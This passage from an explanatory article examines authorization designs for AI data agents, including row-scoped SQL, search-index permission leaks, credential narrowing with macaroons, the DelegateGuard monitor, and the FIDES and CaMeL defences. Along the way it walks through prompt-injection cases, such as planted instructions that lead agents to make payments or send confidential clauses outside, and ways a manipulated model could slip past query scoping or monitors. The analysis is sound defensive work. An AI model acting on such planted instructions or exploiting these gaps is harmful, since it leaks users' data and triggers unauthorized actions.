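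Databricks recommends testing with a temporary tool that reports which identity the agent is using, then repeating the test with a second person, since one correct name doesn't prove that each request runs as the person who made it. User authorization is still in public preview, so an administrator has to turn it on.

### Split-Plane SQL

PAR serves more than 300 restaurant businesses from one Databricks warehouse. It runs every query through a single service principal instead of connecting as each customer's user, and PAR's own code limits access. Each request carries IDs for the brand group, the restaurant business and the individual user. PAR signs the request so that changing an ID in transit invalidates the request.

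PAR Technology calls its method Split-Plane SQL. Before the model sees anything, ordinary code writes subqueries that select the rows this user may read. The model receives only the names and columns of those subqueries and writes the rest. A shortened version, with simpler names than PAR's, looks like this:

```sql
WITH my_locations AS (
    SELECT location_id FROM location_access WHERE admin_id = 7042
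),
my_sales AS (
    SELECT * FROM store_sales
    WHERE location_id IN (SELECT location_id FROM my_locations)
)
-- The model writes only what follows
SELECT SUM(revenue) FROM my_sales;
```

This defends well against a model that omits a filter, because the filter is already there, but less well against a model that someone has manipulated. PAR claims that even a fully jailbroken model "cannot reference tables it has not been shown". However, the service principal must be able to read `store_sales`, or the subquery would fail. If the model ended the query with `FROM store_sales`, the database would apparently add up every restaurant's sales and leave `my_sales` unused.

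This is less likely because the model would have to know or guess the table's name, but it's still possible. The models that Fei and colleagues tested guessed the names of hidden columns, and a customer could also type a likely table name into a question. PAR may reject queries that name other tables, but it describes no such check. A program that reads the model's SQL and allows only the prepared subqueries would prevent this. PAR could also copy the permitted rows into a temporary table and run the model's part under an account that can read nothing else, though this would slow down every question.

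PAR also goes too far in describing its three layers of protection as independent and deterministic. The second layer isn't deterministic, because it is a language model that judges whether a question concerns a supported business measure. The third layer isn't independent of the first, because it builds its filters from the three IDs that the first protects. If an attacker could substitute another customer's valid IDs, those filters would select that customer's rows.

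PAR also says that a request for another business's data causes a database error. But in ordinary SQL, a query that matches no rows returns an empty result without an error. The data stays safe, but the agent might tell the user that the other business had no sales.

PAR Technology reports more than 50,000 production queries with no exposure of one customer's data to another, but it doesn't explain how it looks for exposures. If PAR would have noticed every exposure and the queries were a random sample, the true rate would be below about 0.006%, with 95% confidence. Most of those queries presumably came from people asking about their own restaurants, so they are weak evidence of whether the system would withstand a deliberate attack.

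| | Skipper | Databricks user authorization | PAR |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identity that runs the query | The employee | The user | A service principal |
| Location of the row limits | A policy that Trino reads | Row filters in Unity Catalog | Subqueries that PAR's code writes |
| Failure to test for | A script that can change the identity or lift redaction | A missing token | SQL that names an original table |

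### Two correct totals

PAR Technology illustrates its goal with two users who ask for last week's total sales. A franchise owner with two locations should get $84,000, and a brand manager responsible for all 200 should get $9.2 million. The model can write the same SQL for both.

| Result | Franchise owner | Brand manager |
|---|---|---|
| Locations included | 2 | 200 |
| Total sales | $84,000 | $9.2 million |
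| Average per location | $42,000 | $46,000 |
| The owner's share of the total | 100% | 0.9% |

Both totals are correct for the rows they add up, but the other two lines in the owner's column could mislead her. Suppose her two restaurants sold $45,000 and $39,000, an average of $42,000. If she asks whether the first did better than average, the agent compares $45,000 with $42,000 and says yes, although the chain's average is $46,000. If she asks what share of the chain's sales came from her restaurants, it divides $84,000 by $84,000 and answers 100%.

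The access rules worked correctly in both cases. A row filter doesn't indicate that it has removed rows, so the model can't tell that 198 locations are missing. An agent that serves users with different rights should therefore label its totals, for example "sales at the 2 locations you can access". The code that applied the limit should generate the label, because the model would only be guessing. If franchise owners ought to know the chain's average, someone with authority over the data can publish it separately, as the payroll company could with its average salary.

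### Search indexes with their builder's view

Agents also search text, because much of a company's information is in documents. A search index stores copies of passages so that related ones can be found quickly, and the agent puts the best matches in the model's context. The account that builds the index needs to read everything in it. The rules on the original table don't automatically apply to the copy, as with the tokens that Supabase's assistant copied into a support ticket.

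Snowflake's search product, Cortex Search, runs with owner's rights. According to Snowflake's *Cortex Search*, the product saves the results of the owner's query in a separate table, and users need permission for the search service but not for the original data.

*Unexpected behavior in Snowflake's Cortex AI* (April 2025), from the data security vendor Cyera, demonstrates the effect with a salary table. A masking rule showed real salaries to administrators and asterisks to everyone else. An administrator built a search service over the table and let an analyst use it. The analyst saw asterisks when querying the table but real salaries when using the search service. Snowflake responded by clarifying its documentation, and Cyera describes the problem as one that administrators can avoid.

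Snowflake's *CREATE CORTEX SEARCH SERVICE* now includes a setting that makes a search service apply its source table's row and masking rules to each caller. The setting is off by default and works only for searches made through two SQL functions. It does not cover agents that search through Snowflake's Python interface, as the one in Snowflake's own example does. *How to Build a Governed RAG Agent in Snowflake*, from the access-control vendor Immuta, recommends avoiding Cortex Search for this reason. Its design keeps the passages in an ordinary table, where row rules apply, and gives each user's session a temporary role.

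Both approaches are forms of permission filtering at retrieval, in which the index returns only passages that the requesting user may read. The index must store who may read each passage and receive the user's identity from the application. Filtering before selecting the best matches avoids losing results that the user may read. If the index instead selects the five best matches and then removes those the user may not read, it could return nothing, even when the sixth and seventh matches are open to her.

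Microsoft's Azure AI Search requires both the application's role and the user's identity before it returns a protected document. If it can't check permissions because the company directory is unavailable, it returns an error and no results. This is a better way to fail than that of Databricks' connection function, and developers who write their own filters should copy it.

### Old permissions

A filter is only as current as the permissions it uses. In one of Snowflake's examples, the index checks the source table for changes about once a day. Suppose the payroll company builds such an index, lists the permitted readers of each passage in an extra column, and refreshes the index at 1 a.m. each day. If a clerk loses payroll access at noon, she can keep finding payroll documents through the agent until the next refresh, 13 hours later.

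The company could instead store the permitted group with each passage and look up the clerk's membership when she searches, as Lifeguard does for Skipper's queries. Removing her from the group would then take effect almost at once. But when a manager moves a file from a shared folder to a restricted one, the index keeps the old group until the next refresh.

Rules that developers copy into an application cause the same problem. Databricks warns in a post on its community site that these copies stop matching the rules in Unity Catalog, and gives this as one reason to pass on the user's identity.

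Delays can also affect new permissions. Immuta found that a permission granted through its software could take about ten minutes to reach a Databricks token, and the agent's queries failed in the meantime. The failed queries are a nuisance, but nobody sees data they shouldn't. A company that can't avoid delays should at least make removals take effect faster than grants.

### Caches, reports and memory

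An application may save answers to avoid running the same query twice. If it stores them by the text of the question alone, the franchise owner who asks for last week's sales after the brand manager does will get the brand manager's answer, $9.2 million.

If a cache stores answers by their SQL text, PAR's design is safer than the other two because its finished query contains the user's IDs and so differs for each person. With Skipper or Databricks, two users may send identical SQL and depend on the database to treat them differently. A cache in front of the database must therefore include the user's identity or permissions in its key, and discard the answer when those permissions change. None of the three companies reports having made this mistake.

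Saved reports, too, can run with either the caller's or the owner's rights. Cloudflare checks a teammate's access when she opens a saved query, because her groups may have changed since a colleague shared it. Snowflake says shared apps in its Streamlit product run with the owner's privileges, so every viewer gets what the owner's role can fetch. TagoIO, a platform for connected devices, makes the same choice. Its documentation states plainly that a user allowed to run a saved query gets the full result, and no rule removes rows or columns.

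Even Cloudflare's check may not be enough for dashboards. The company checks viewers "against the underlying tables", but two people with access to the same table may be entitled to see different rows. To keep a viewer from seeing rows she isn't entitled to, the dashboard has to rerun the query with that viewer's permissions, and Cloudflare doesn't say whether it does.

Memory is harder to control because people don't think of it as a report. Cloudflare says that storing employees' corrections improved Skipper's answers more than it expected, but doesn't say who can read them. If a payroll clerk writes "leave out the 40,000 severance payment to Maria when you total March", and the agent saves this for everyone, the next employee who asks about March may learn of the payment without querying any table. Other corrections, like "ignore tables with this tag", are harmless to share. Keeping memories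 private would prevent the leak, but the agent would have to relearn useful corrections for each user. A company could instead share only corrections that a person has reviewed.

PAR uses feedback from its customers to improve the model that checks their questions, and recommends removing personal information from the feedback first. That step would leave in a comment such as "the total should be $9.2 million", which contains no personal information.

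### Filtering the answer

If a company leaves all these copies alone and only filters confidential text out of the agent's final answer, the model will still have read that text. Before writing any answer, it could have put the text in a web request or a message through another tool, as the agents in the GitHub cases did. An agent on Databricks also normally records traces of its work under the app's identity. If those traces include search results, anyone allowed to read them may see what the filter removed.

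It is also hard to remove restricted data from an answer. A filter that looks for a colleague's salary of 61,980 will catch the number, but it will probably miss "just under sixty-two thousand" or "about a fifth more than you earn". A second model might catch some of these, but it would be unreliable, as such judges were on access decisions. The Agent Stack's *The Data Agent Stack*, a newsletter series on data agents, makes the general point that "a successful query is not proof of an authorized answer", because data can leak while the agent retrieves, remembers or publishes it.

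Redaction works when it happens before the data reaches the model. Trino hides sensitive columns before it returns a result, so unless someone lifts the redaction, Skipper's model never receives the values and can't repeat them in any wording. Once an employee lifts it, even for a good reason, the real values are in the model's context, and Trino can't control where the model sends them.

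## Authority passed from one agent to another: DelegateGuard

Skipper's row limits work because the employee's identity reaches the database with the query. This is harder to arrange when one agent takes a request and another carries it out. In many systems, an orchestrator agent divides a task among sub-agents that have their own tools. If the orchestrator passes on the task without the user's limits, a sub-agent may do something the user never allowed.

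### An invoice summary that ends in a payment

Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026), in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, describe how this can happen:

1. A user permits an orchestrator to summarize the invoices in an inbox.
2. The orchestrator reads a message that an outsider sent.
3. The message contains an instruction to make a payment.
4. The orchestrator passes the instruction to a finance agent but leaves out that the user allowed only reading.
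5. The payment system receives a valid credential and pays.
6. The payment system has verified the caller, but it has no way to tell that an outsider's message caused the payment.

The finance agent is a confused deputy. Its job is to make payments, and a genuine request from the orchestrator would presumably have looked the same as the one it received. The read-only limit existed only in the user's instructions to the orchestrator, and it was lost when the orchestrator described the task to another agent.

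Passing on the user's token may not solve this. According to an O'Reilly article whose author promotes his own delegation protocol, each additional agent usually either reuses the original token, which permits too much, or has no token, so nobody can trace what it did.

### Narrowing a credential at each hop

With attenuation, the user's limits would still apply as the task passes from agent to agent. Suppose a finance manager is allowed to read, annotate and pay all supplier invoices. At 10:00 she asks for a summary of October's invoices, and the work passes through three agents.

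| Holder | Actions | Invoices | Purpose | Expires |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The manager | Read, annotate, pay | All | Any | No fixed time |
| Orchestrator | Read, annotate | October's | Summarize October | 11:00 |
| Totals agent | Read | October's from one supplier | Add up that supplier's invoices for the summary | 10:20 |
| Translation agent | Read | Invoice 4417 | Translate that invoice for the total | 10:05 |

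If P₀ is the set of things the manager may do and P₁, P₂ and P₃ are the sets for the three agents, then

P₃ ⊆ P₂ ⊆ P₁ ⊆ P₀.

None of the agents' delegated credentials allows a payment, so an injected instruction to pay should fail whichever agent reads it, provided the payment system accepts only those credentials. If the orchestrator forwards the instruction to a finance agent with its own service account, and the payment system accepts that account, the payment can go through despite the limits in the table.

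Attenuation also requires an agent to hold any permission it passes on, which is sometimes undesirable. In the O'Reilly article, a payer asks a bookkeeping agent to make a payment, and the bookkeeping agent asks a banking agent to execute it. Only the banking agent should have authority over the bank account. Under strict attenuation, the bookkeeping agent would need permission to make the payment before it could delegate that permission, and could then misuse it. The banking agent could instead have its own permission and check that an authorized payer made the request, as Ritchie's accounting program checked who was asking. Without a reliable check, the company would have the same problem as in the invoice example.

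### Limits that a holder can add but not remove

A sub-agent under an attacker's influence might try to delete the limits from its credential. *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes a credential that prevents this. A macaroon contains a list of limits, called caveats, and a signature made with HMAC. HMAC takes a key and a message and returns a short code that nobody can produce without the key.

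The service that protects the invoices has a secret key K. With two limits, the signatures look like this:

```
s0 = HMAC(K,  "macaroon 81")
s1 = HMAC(s0, "month = October")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "action = read")
```

Each signature is the key for the next. If the orchestrator holds the macaroon signed with s1, it can add "action = read", compute s2, and give the totals agent the list of limits and s2, but not s1. The totals agent can use s2 as a key to add another limit, but it can't remove "action = read", because that would require s1, and HMAC can't be reversed to get s1 from s2. When an agent sends the macaroon with a request, the service recomputes the signatures from K, which exposes any altered list, and checks the request against every limit. An agent can add a later expiry time, but this doesn't extend its access because the earlier one still applies.

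The orchestrator can do all this without contacting the service. In an example from Birgisson and colleagues, a web forum has access to blocks 100 to 500 of a storage service. The forum gives a user a macaroon for block 235 that works from only one network address and for a shorter time. With token exchange, the forum would have to ask a server for a new token.

Macaroons have some weaknesses for agents. Anyone who obtains one can use it unless one of its limits prevents that. The orchestrator also keeps its wider macaroon after issuing a narrower one, and if it leaves the wider one in memory shared by the agents, the totals agent can use it. Only a service that knows K can verify a macaroon, which is inconvenient when agents from several companies work together.

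Biscuit, a newer token format, solves the last problem by using public-key signatures, which anyone with the issuer's public key can verify. A holder adds limits in a new block, and a token with a changed or missing block fails verification. In an example from its documentation, the first block lets `user_1234` open `file1` until a given date, and an added block restricts use to the local machine. *AIP* (2026), which proposes a protocol built on Biscuit, points out that the format alone doesn't establish who an agent is, and that separate deployments of plain Biscuit can't readily work together.

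The signatures protect the limits, but someone still has to choose what those limits are. *CAPMAS* (2026), which uses macaroons between agents, calls it intractable to derive perfectly minimal permissions from any request in ordinary language. It uses a trained model to find the permissions whose descriptions are closest in meaning to the request. This takes less computation than asking a large model, but a permission can resemble a request without being necessary for it. The service must also be able to check each limit. An invoice system can check a month or an invoice number, but it can't check whether an agent is reading an invoice to summarize it or to copy it elsewhere.

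### What multi-agent systems leave out

Although macaroons are more than a decade old, common agent frameworks provide nothing like them by default. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, examined three frameworks and the MCP authorization specification for protection against four threats:

- an agent that misuses its authority on an attacker's instruction
- a stolen token
- an agent that gains permissions its task doesn't need
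- a compromised sub-agent with too much access

DelegateGuard assumes that the attacker controls everything the model writes, so it gives a framework no credit for using a model that usually refuses bad instructions. It also checks frameworks for eight features, including narrowing authority at each hop, revocation, an audit log, and access decisions made outside the model.

| System | Method | Threats prevented by default | Features provided |
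|---|---|---|---|
| LangGraph | Ran a scripted agent | None | None |
| CrewAI | Inspected the code | None | None |
| AutoGen | Inspected the code | None | None |
| MCP authorization | Read the specification | Token theft, in part | Short-lived tokens, and five others in part |

Dantuluri and Sundi work for VotalAI, which sells a product that supplies the missing controls. They acknowledge that none of the frameworks is presented as an authorization system, so their finding is about the frameworks' defaults, as in Mellafe Zuvic's audit. They rate MCP inconsistently. One table lists partial support for key rotation and revocation but no audit log, while another lists partial support for auditing but none for key rotation or revocation.

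According to both tables, MCP doesn't narrow authority between agents. Surapani and colleagues came to the same conclusion and found the same gap in Amazon Bedrock Agents, where one agent calls another under permissions attached to its own role, with no narrowed version of what the user delegated.

Dantuluri and Sundi built a broker to show that existing techniques could close the gap. It issues a narrower token at each hop and ties it to the receiving agent. In 2,000 simulated scenarios, a compromised sub-agent could take an average of 1.5 of 8,100 possible actions, compared with all 8,100 when agents shared one broad token. The 1.5 is just the average size of the delegated tasks. The more useful result is that a compromised agent's reach does not grow as the company adds systems. The broker also rejected all 200,000 forged tokens, as any sound signature scheme would.

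Dantuluri and Sundi also report that the broker blocks confused-deputy attacks. Like WorkOS's intersection rule, it does so only when the attack needs something outside the agent's permissions.

### DelegateGuard's grants

*DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) adds limits on where agents may send data. A monitor outside the model checks every tool call, message between agents, memory write and new delegation. Software called a trusted adapter turns the user's request into a first grant, using a template for each kind of task. The connectors that supply the data also supply its labels, such as "confidential contract".

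In their main example, a user asks an orchestrator to summarize a confidential contract, and the orchestrator gives the formatting to another agent. (The delegation depths below are illustrative.)

| Part of the grant | Orchestrator | Formatting agent |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | `contract.summarize` | `contract.summarize/format` |
| Data labels | Confidential contract | Confidential contract |
| Operations | Read, transform, transmit, delegate | Transform, transmit |
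| Destinations | Reply to the user, internal systems | Reply to the user |
| Further delegations allowed | 1 | 0 |

The monitor permits an action only if the agent holds the grant and the purpose, operation, labels and destination all fall within it. A new grant can't add anything its parent lacks, and its delegation depth must be lower than the parent's. A clause planted in the contract tells the agent to send the restrictive covenants to an outside web address. If the formatting agent tries to send them, the monitor blocks it because the agent's grant doesn't include that address. The monitor also blocks the orchestrator from creating a sub-agent with permission to use the address.

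The monitor stores grants in its own table, so agents can't narrow them offline as they can with macaroons, but this makes revocation simple. When a user cancels a task, the monitor revokes the orchestrator's grant and every grant derived from it, so a sub-agent that starts after the cancellation can't use its grant.

The orchestrator remains the most attractive target because it must hold every permission it delegates. An attacker who misleads it could have the confidential clauses sent to any internal destination its grant allows, even though the formatting agent could not send them there.

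### Attacks outside and inside the grant

Tran-Truong and colleagues tested five office tasks: answering email, scheduling, summarizing contracts, reviewing code and writing customer notes. They planted instructions in tool results, shared memory or messages between agents. The instructions told an agent to send data outside, create a more powerful sub-agent, or act after its authority was revoked. They paired each of the 45 attacks with a legitimate version of the task.

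Two small models from 2024 proposed the attacker's action in 42 and 44 of the 45 cases. DelegateGuard blocked all of these and allowed all 45 legitimate actions. In the second test, which used prepared actions, each attack plainly broke one of DelegateGuard's rules, so the researchers rightly call it a check that the program follows its own rules. A run over 517,401 real emails also had no errors, but DelegateGuard looks only at labels and destinations, so the variety of the emails made little difference.

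A harder test used 26 attacks, most of which stayed within what the grant appeared to allow. Some declared that secret data had no label, and others passed it to another agent through shared memory. The researchers compared DelegateGuard with four alternatives.

| Protection | Attacks that leaked the secret (of 26) | Legitimate tasks blocked (of 5) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 18 | 0 |
| Fixed list of destinations | 3 | 0 |
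| Rules on which labels may reach which destinations | 3 | 0 |
| Filter that blocks any output containing the secret | 0 | 4 |
| DelegateGuard | 3 | 0 |

DelegateGuard did no better than a fixed list of destinations, except in ten additional cases where it refused actions that the list allowed. In five of these, an agent tried to finish its work after the user had canceled the task. In the other five, an agent tried to send the wrong data to a permitted destination.

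The five refusals for wrong data depend on accurate labels. Tran-Truong and colleagues say that in their design an agent can't remove a label by leaving it out, but their harder test assumes the monitor relies on labels the agent declares. A company would need to attach labels in code that the agent can't influence.

The monitor also enforces grants that contain mistakes. When the researchers added a single outside address to the first grant for convenience, 30 of the original 45 attacks succeeded. The other 15 still failed because they relied on revoked authority. Some other mistakes, such as leaving out permission to transmit, blocked every legitimate task instead.

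In complete workflows, DelegateGuard cut the share of attacks that leaked data from 73% to 20% without blocking any legitimate task. In a separate test, where a model could retry after a refusal, the rate was also 20% (9 of 45 attacked runs). The nine leaks came from the test's nine attacked code reviews, where the agent's job is to post a comment that outsiders can read. The 20% therefore reflects the share of tasks that had a public destination, and a company whose agents mostly write in public could expect a much higher rate.

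### Why the monitor can't stop a public leak

Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that no adjustment to the rules would have stopped the code-review leaks. Their Proposition 1 covers any monitor that bases its decisions on the holder, purpose, labels, operation, destination and chain of grants, and ignores the content and quantity of what an agent sends. If outsiders can see an authorized destination, such a monitor will permit some leak through it.

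The proof is short:

1. The destination is authorized, so the monitor permits some harmless message there, such as "Please add a test for this function."
2. Replace the text with details of an unpublished security flaw. Keep the agent, purpose, labels, operation and destination the same.
3. Nothing the monitor examines has changed, so it permits this message too.
4. An outsider reads it.

The result follows almost directly from the fact that a decision can't depend on something the monitor never examines. It applies to many access rules, including the ones in GitLost, where the agent had permission to post a comment regardless of its content.

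The second step requires both messages to have the same labels. If the harmless comment carried no confidential label and the agent couldn't falsify labels, the monitor could distinguish the two. But the agent needs the confidential material to do these code reviews, so the harmless comment carries the label too. Labels and controlled release (declassification) therefore have to work together. The other option is to filter the text, but the filter tested also blocked four of the five legitimate tasks.

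DelegateGuard has a similar problem with payments, because its rules include a destination but no amount. If a grant lets the finance agent pay a certain supplier, the monitor would approve a payment of €40 or €40,000. An amount limit like ScopeGate's would catch the larger payment if someone had set it below €40,000.

### When a user loses access during a task

Suppose the finance manager asks the orchestrator to schedule payments for October's invoices. At noon the company withdraws her permission to pay, but the finance agent has already placed a payment in the bank's queue for 17:00. The orchestrator confirms that it has canceled the task, the authorization server revokes its token, and the program exits. The bank could still pay at 17:00 because it has already accepted the payment and may not check the token again.

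Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents*, use a case of this kind to show that these three signals together don't prove the work has stopped. Authority can survive in queued messages, timers, reservations and credentials that the first agent passed on. Applied to the manager's payments, their method would go roughly like this:

1. Stop issuing new credentials based on her permission.
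2. Make the bank and every other system that can act refuse further requests that depend on it.
3. Find the work already in progress, then cancel it or move it to someone else's valid authority.
4. List the payments the bank accepted before it began to refuse them.
5. Report the shutdown as complete only if every system has answered. If one has not, its state is unknown, however long the company has waited.

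The second step matters most. In Zhu and Wang's simulations, a scheduled action still went through in two runs where only the task was canceled and in one where only the authority behind it was withdrawn. The receiving system rejected the action in two runs that also set up a block there. The simulations involved no real bank or other provider. A provider that offers no way to block or query its queue can't give the company the necessary proof.

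The third step is difficult when agents are shared. If the finance agent also works for a colleague whose access is still valid, shutting it down would stop the colleague's payments too. *VERA* (2026) argues for revoking only the withdrawn link and keeping any agent that has another valid path to a user. But the agent must not finish the manager's payments under the colleague's authority just because it has authority from both. Zhu and Wang allow work to continue only after an explicit switch to authority that is sufficient without the manager's. In DelegateGuard, each grant has at most one parent, so the agent would hold a separate grant for each user. Canceling the manager's grant would leave the colleague's intact. But if the two grants had the same purpose and destinations, the monitor might not detect that the agent was using the colleague's grant for the manager's work.

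Tokens that agents narrow offline are harder to revoke, because the issuer may not know how many narrower versions exist. *The Bureaucracy of Speed* (2026) reports that the OpenID Foundation, which develops login standards, calls this problem "largely unsolved". Birgisson and colleagues suggest very short lifetimes, or a caveat that requires fresh proof from a revocation service. Requiring proof restores control, but it also brings back the network request that offline tokens were meant to avoid. Even a short lifetime may be too long for an agent. At ten calls a second, an agent with a five-minute token could make 3,000 calls after the company withdraws the user's access. Surapani and colleagues therefore include a maximum number of uses among their defences.

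The company also has to decide whether to stop the work. If the manager moved to another department and had properly approved the October payments, canceling them could leave suppliers unpaid. Another authorized person could review them and take them over. If the company suspects that someone stole her account, it should block the payments first and then investigate. *Agent-ZTA* (2026) separates the authority an agent has received from the part it may currently use, so a company can suspend an agent without permanently revoking its grant.

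Zhou and Zhang point out that revocation can block future reads, but information already stored needs its own controls, and information already delivered can't be recalled. The orchestrator may have saved the supplier's bank details in its memory, and the totals agent may have put them in a spreadsheet. If the company knows where those copies are, it can delete them or restrict who may open them.

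## Labels that follow data through the model: FIDES and CaMeL

Row-level security and permission filters on a search index have no effect on text that is already in a model's context. If an agent reads a salary and puts it in an email, the mail server checks whether the agent may send email, but nothing checks whether the recipient may read the salary. To enforce the salary's read permissions, software outside the model would have to attach them to the salary, apply them to anything the model derives from it, and check them wherever data can leave the system. This is information-flow control, which researchers have studied since the 1970s. In 2025, two research systems, FIDES and CaMeL, applied it to AI agents.

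### Combining labels

A confidentiality label records who is allowed to read a piece of data. An integrity label records who might have influenced it or, in a simpler form, whether its source is trusted. When an agent produces something from several inputs, the output gets the strictest combination of their labels.

Say Alice and Bob may read a budget, and Bob and Carol may read a hiring plan. Bob asks an agent to summarize both files on one page. The permitted readers of the summary are

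{Alice, Bob} ∩ {Bob, Carol} = {Bob}.

Only Bob may receive the summary, because Alice might learn about the hiring plan from it and Carol might learn about the budget. If the model used only the budget, Alice could safely read the summary, but the rule is based on what the summary might contain.

Integrity labels combine by union instead. If Alice can edit the budget and an outside recruiter can edit the hiring plan, either may have influenced the summary. Both rules are part of FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues built at Microsoft and describe in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025). Before data leaves, FIDES can require every recipient to be on the data's reader list. GitHub doesn't compare readers this way when an agent copies private text to a public page. FIDES can do so even after a model has reworded the text or mixed it with other sources.

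Siu and colleagues include a similar requirement, data isolation, among their four properties of a secure agent. If a tool call sends data to a recipient d, then for every source s of that data,

(s, d) ∈ R,

where R again contains the permitted connections. With reader lists, a recipient passes this test exactly when she is in the intersection. Their example is a cooking assistant that learns one user's grocery budget and mentions it to another user in a later session. Benchmarks usually reset an agent's context between tasks, so they can't detect this kind of leak.

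### Tracing an output to its inputs

Testing data isolation requires knowing where the data came from. Siu and colleagues define a source attribution function, which maps each input to its sources, and an instruction attribution function, which identifies the inputs that the agent followed as instructions. Both functions are idealized, as is their test of whether an action serves the user's objective.

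Tracking which data influenced a result is fairly easy in ordinary software. If a program computes `total = a + b`, the total depends on `a` and `b`. A language model computes each word by mixing together everything in its context, and it keeps no record of which file contributed which phrase. A developer could ask the model which files it used, but the answer would be more generated text, which an injected instruction could also influence.

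The safe fallback is to assume that everything in the context influenced the output. After the agent reads one untrusted email, all its later output is untrusted. If a payroll clerk asks for a colleague's March pay and then asks the agent to send the holiday rules to a new employee, the agent must refuse. Anyone may read the rules, but the pay record's reader list now applies to the whole context, and the new employee isn't on it. Nothing leaks, but the clerk has to start a new conversation for an ordinary task.

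Some researchers try to narrow the label. Costa and colleagues mention a method that finds a smaller set of messages leading to a similar answer, then regenerates the answer from those messages alone. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) lists two newer systems, NeuroTaint, which tracks influence through both models and ordinary code, and Agent-Sentry, which checks whether untrusted sources influenced sensitive arguments of a tool call. Another survey, *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), warns that methods that run the model several times or keep data in tracked variables add substantial running time. FIDES and CaMeL use tracked variables so that the planning model can often avoid reading the restricted text.

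### FIDES: placeholders for untrusted text

FIDES builds on a design that Willison proposed in 2023. One model, the planner, chooses the tool calls. A second, isolated model reads untrusted text but has no tools. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the planner's context, FIDES stores the data in memory and shows the planner a placeholder.

If a user asks the agent to summarize her three latest emails and send the summary to Bob, FIDES proceeds like this:

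1. The planner calls `read_emails`. FIDES stores the untrusted text and returns the placeholder `#read_emails_0`.
2. The planner asks the isolated model to summarize whatever is behind that placeholder.
3. FIDES stores the summary as `#query_llm_0` and gives it the emails' labels.
4. The planner calls `send_message` with Bob as the recipient and `#query_llm_0` as the text.
5. FIDES looks up the text and its labels, and ordinary code checks the call against the policy.
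6. If the call passes, FIDES sends the message.

An outsider's email might contain an instruction to forward the whole mailbox. The planner never reads the instruction, so it can't follow it. The isolated model does read it and might write a false or empty summary, which Bob would then receive.

The policy can contain two main rules. The first allows a consequential action, such as a payment, only if all the data that influenced the call is trusted. The second allows data to be sent only to people on its reader list. Costa and colleagues point out that the second rule doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits where the data can go.

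Hiding text from the planner is a problem when the next step depends on its contents. For example, a user might ask the agent to create a calendar event if an email requests a meeting. The planner can open the placeholder, but its context then takes on the email's label, which may block later calls. It can also have the isolated model answer yes or no. A policy may let the planner act on that answer, since one word is unlikely to contain a working injection.

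FIDES treats the user as trusted, and the version Costa and colleagues tested checks tool calls but not replies to the user. That is reasonable if the agent reads data with the user's own permissions. The payroll company's shared agent, however, leaks data through its replies, so the company would need a policy that covers them too. Costa and colleagues say such a policy is possible.

### CaMeL: a program written in advance

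Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It also has a planner and an isolated model, but the planner writes a whole program before any tool runs. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe the planner as seeing only the user's request and trusted information such as descriptions of the tools. A simplified program might look like this:

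```python
notes = read_file("meeting-notes.txt")
summary = isolated_model("Summarize these notes", notes)
send_message(recipient="Bob", text=summary)
```

CaMeL's interpreter, which runs the program, tracks which data each value came from and can check a policy before every tool call. The planner has already finished writing the program, so text in the notes can't add a second message to it.

The fixed program doesn't protect the values inside it. If the user had asked the agent to send the summary to whoever chaired the meeting, the isolated model would have to find the chair's address in the notes. A planted sentence could make it return an attacker's address, and the unchanged program would send the summary there. Only a policy on the data could prevent this, by checking whether that recipient may read the notes.

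| | FIDES | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| When the planner decides | Before each step | Before any tool runs |
| Where untrusted text is | Behind placeholders | In the program's variables |
| When the next step depends on that text | The planner can open it and accept tighter limits | The program must already contain a branch for it |

### The cost in completed tasks

Both teams tested their systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and Slack messaging. Attackers plant instructions in the data the agent reads. Costa and colleagues used GPT-4o for the results below. The last column is the simple average of the four settings, without attacks.

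| Agent | Policy checks | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | Off | 152 | 84% |
| Ordinary agent with a label on its whole context | On | 0 | 42% |
| FIDES | Off | 21 | 61% |
| FIDES | On | 0 | 50% |

Costa and colleagues emphasize that FIDES completes 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent under the same checks. But it completes 34 points fewer than an unprotected agent. About 24 points of that drop occur before the policy blocks anything, largely because GPT-4o used the placeholders inconsistently and sometimes confused their names. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, the placeholders reduced task completion by only 6.3 points.

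A better model can't complete every task under the policy, because many of the banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy is meant to prevent.

The zeros are good evidence that the check works when the labels are right, but they don't show how often a company would get the labels right. Costa and colleagues labelled a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so the labels were right for this benchmark by construction. They also excluded attacks that changed the text of a message without changing what the agent did.

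Papers differ on how much CaMeL reduces task performance. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that it stopped nearly all AgentDojo attacks with "comparable task performance". Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halved the number of tasks it completed in the banking setting. Their own agent, with its checks on, performed about as well as CaMeL with its checks off. It resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs, but they tested it only on banking.

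In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) object to comparing systems like FIDES and CaMeL with an unprotected agent. They put the drop in completed tasks at up to 30%, but argue that companies rarely let agents act freely. Products such as GitHub Copilot ask a person to approve consequential actions, and labels can show which approvals are unnecessary. Several of the researchers also built FIDES, which their new agent, Prudentia, extends by giving the planner information about the labels and policies.

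They counted the approvals each agent would need on AgentDojo tasks that it completed, without attacks. With OpenAI's o3-mini, the results were:

| Agent | Approvals needed | Tasks completed with no approval |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Labels its whole context | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

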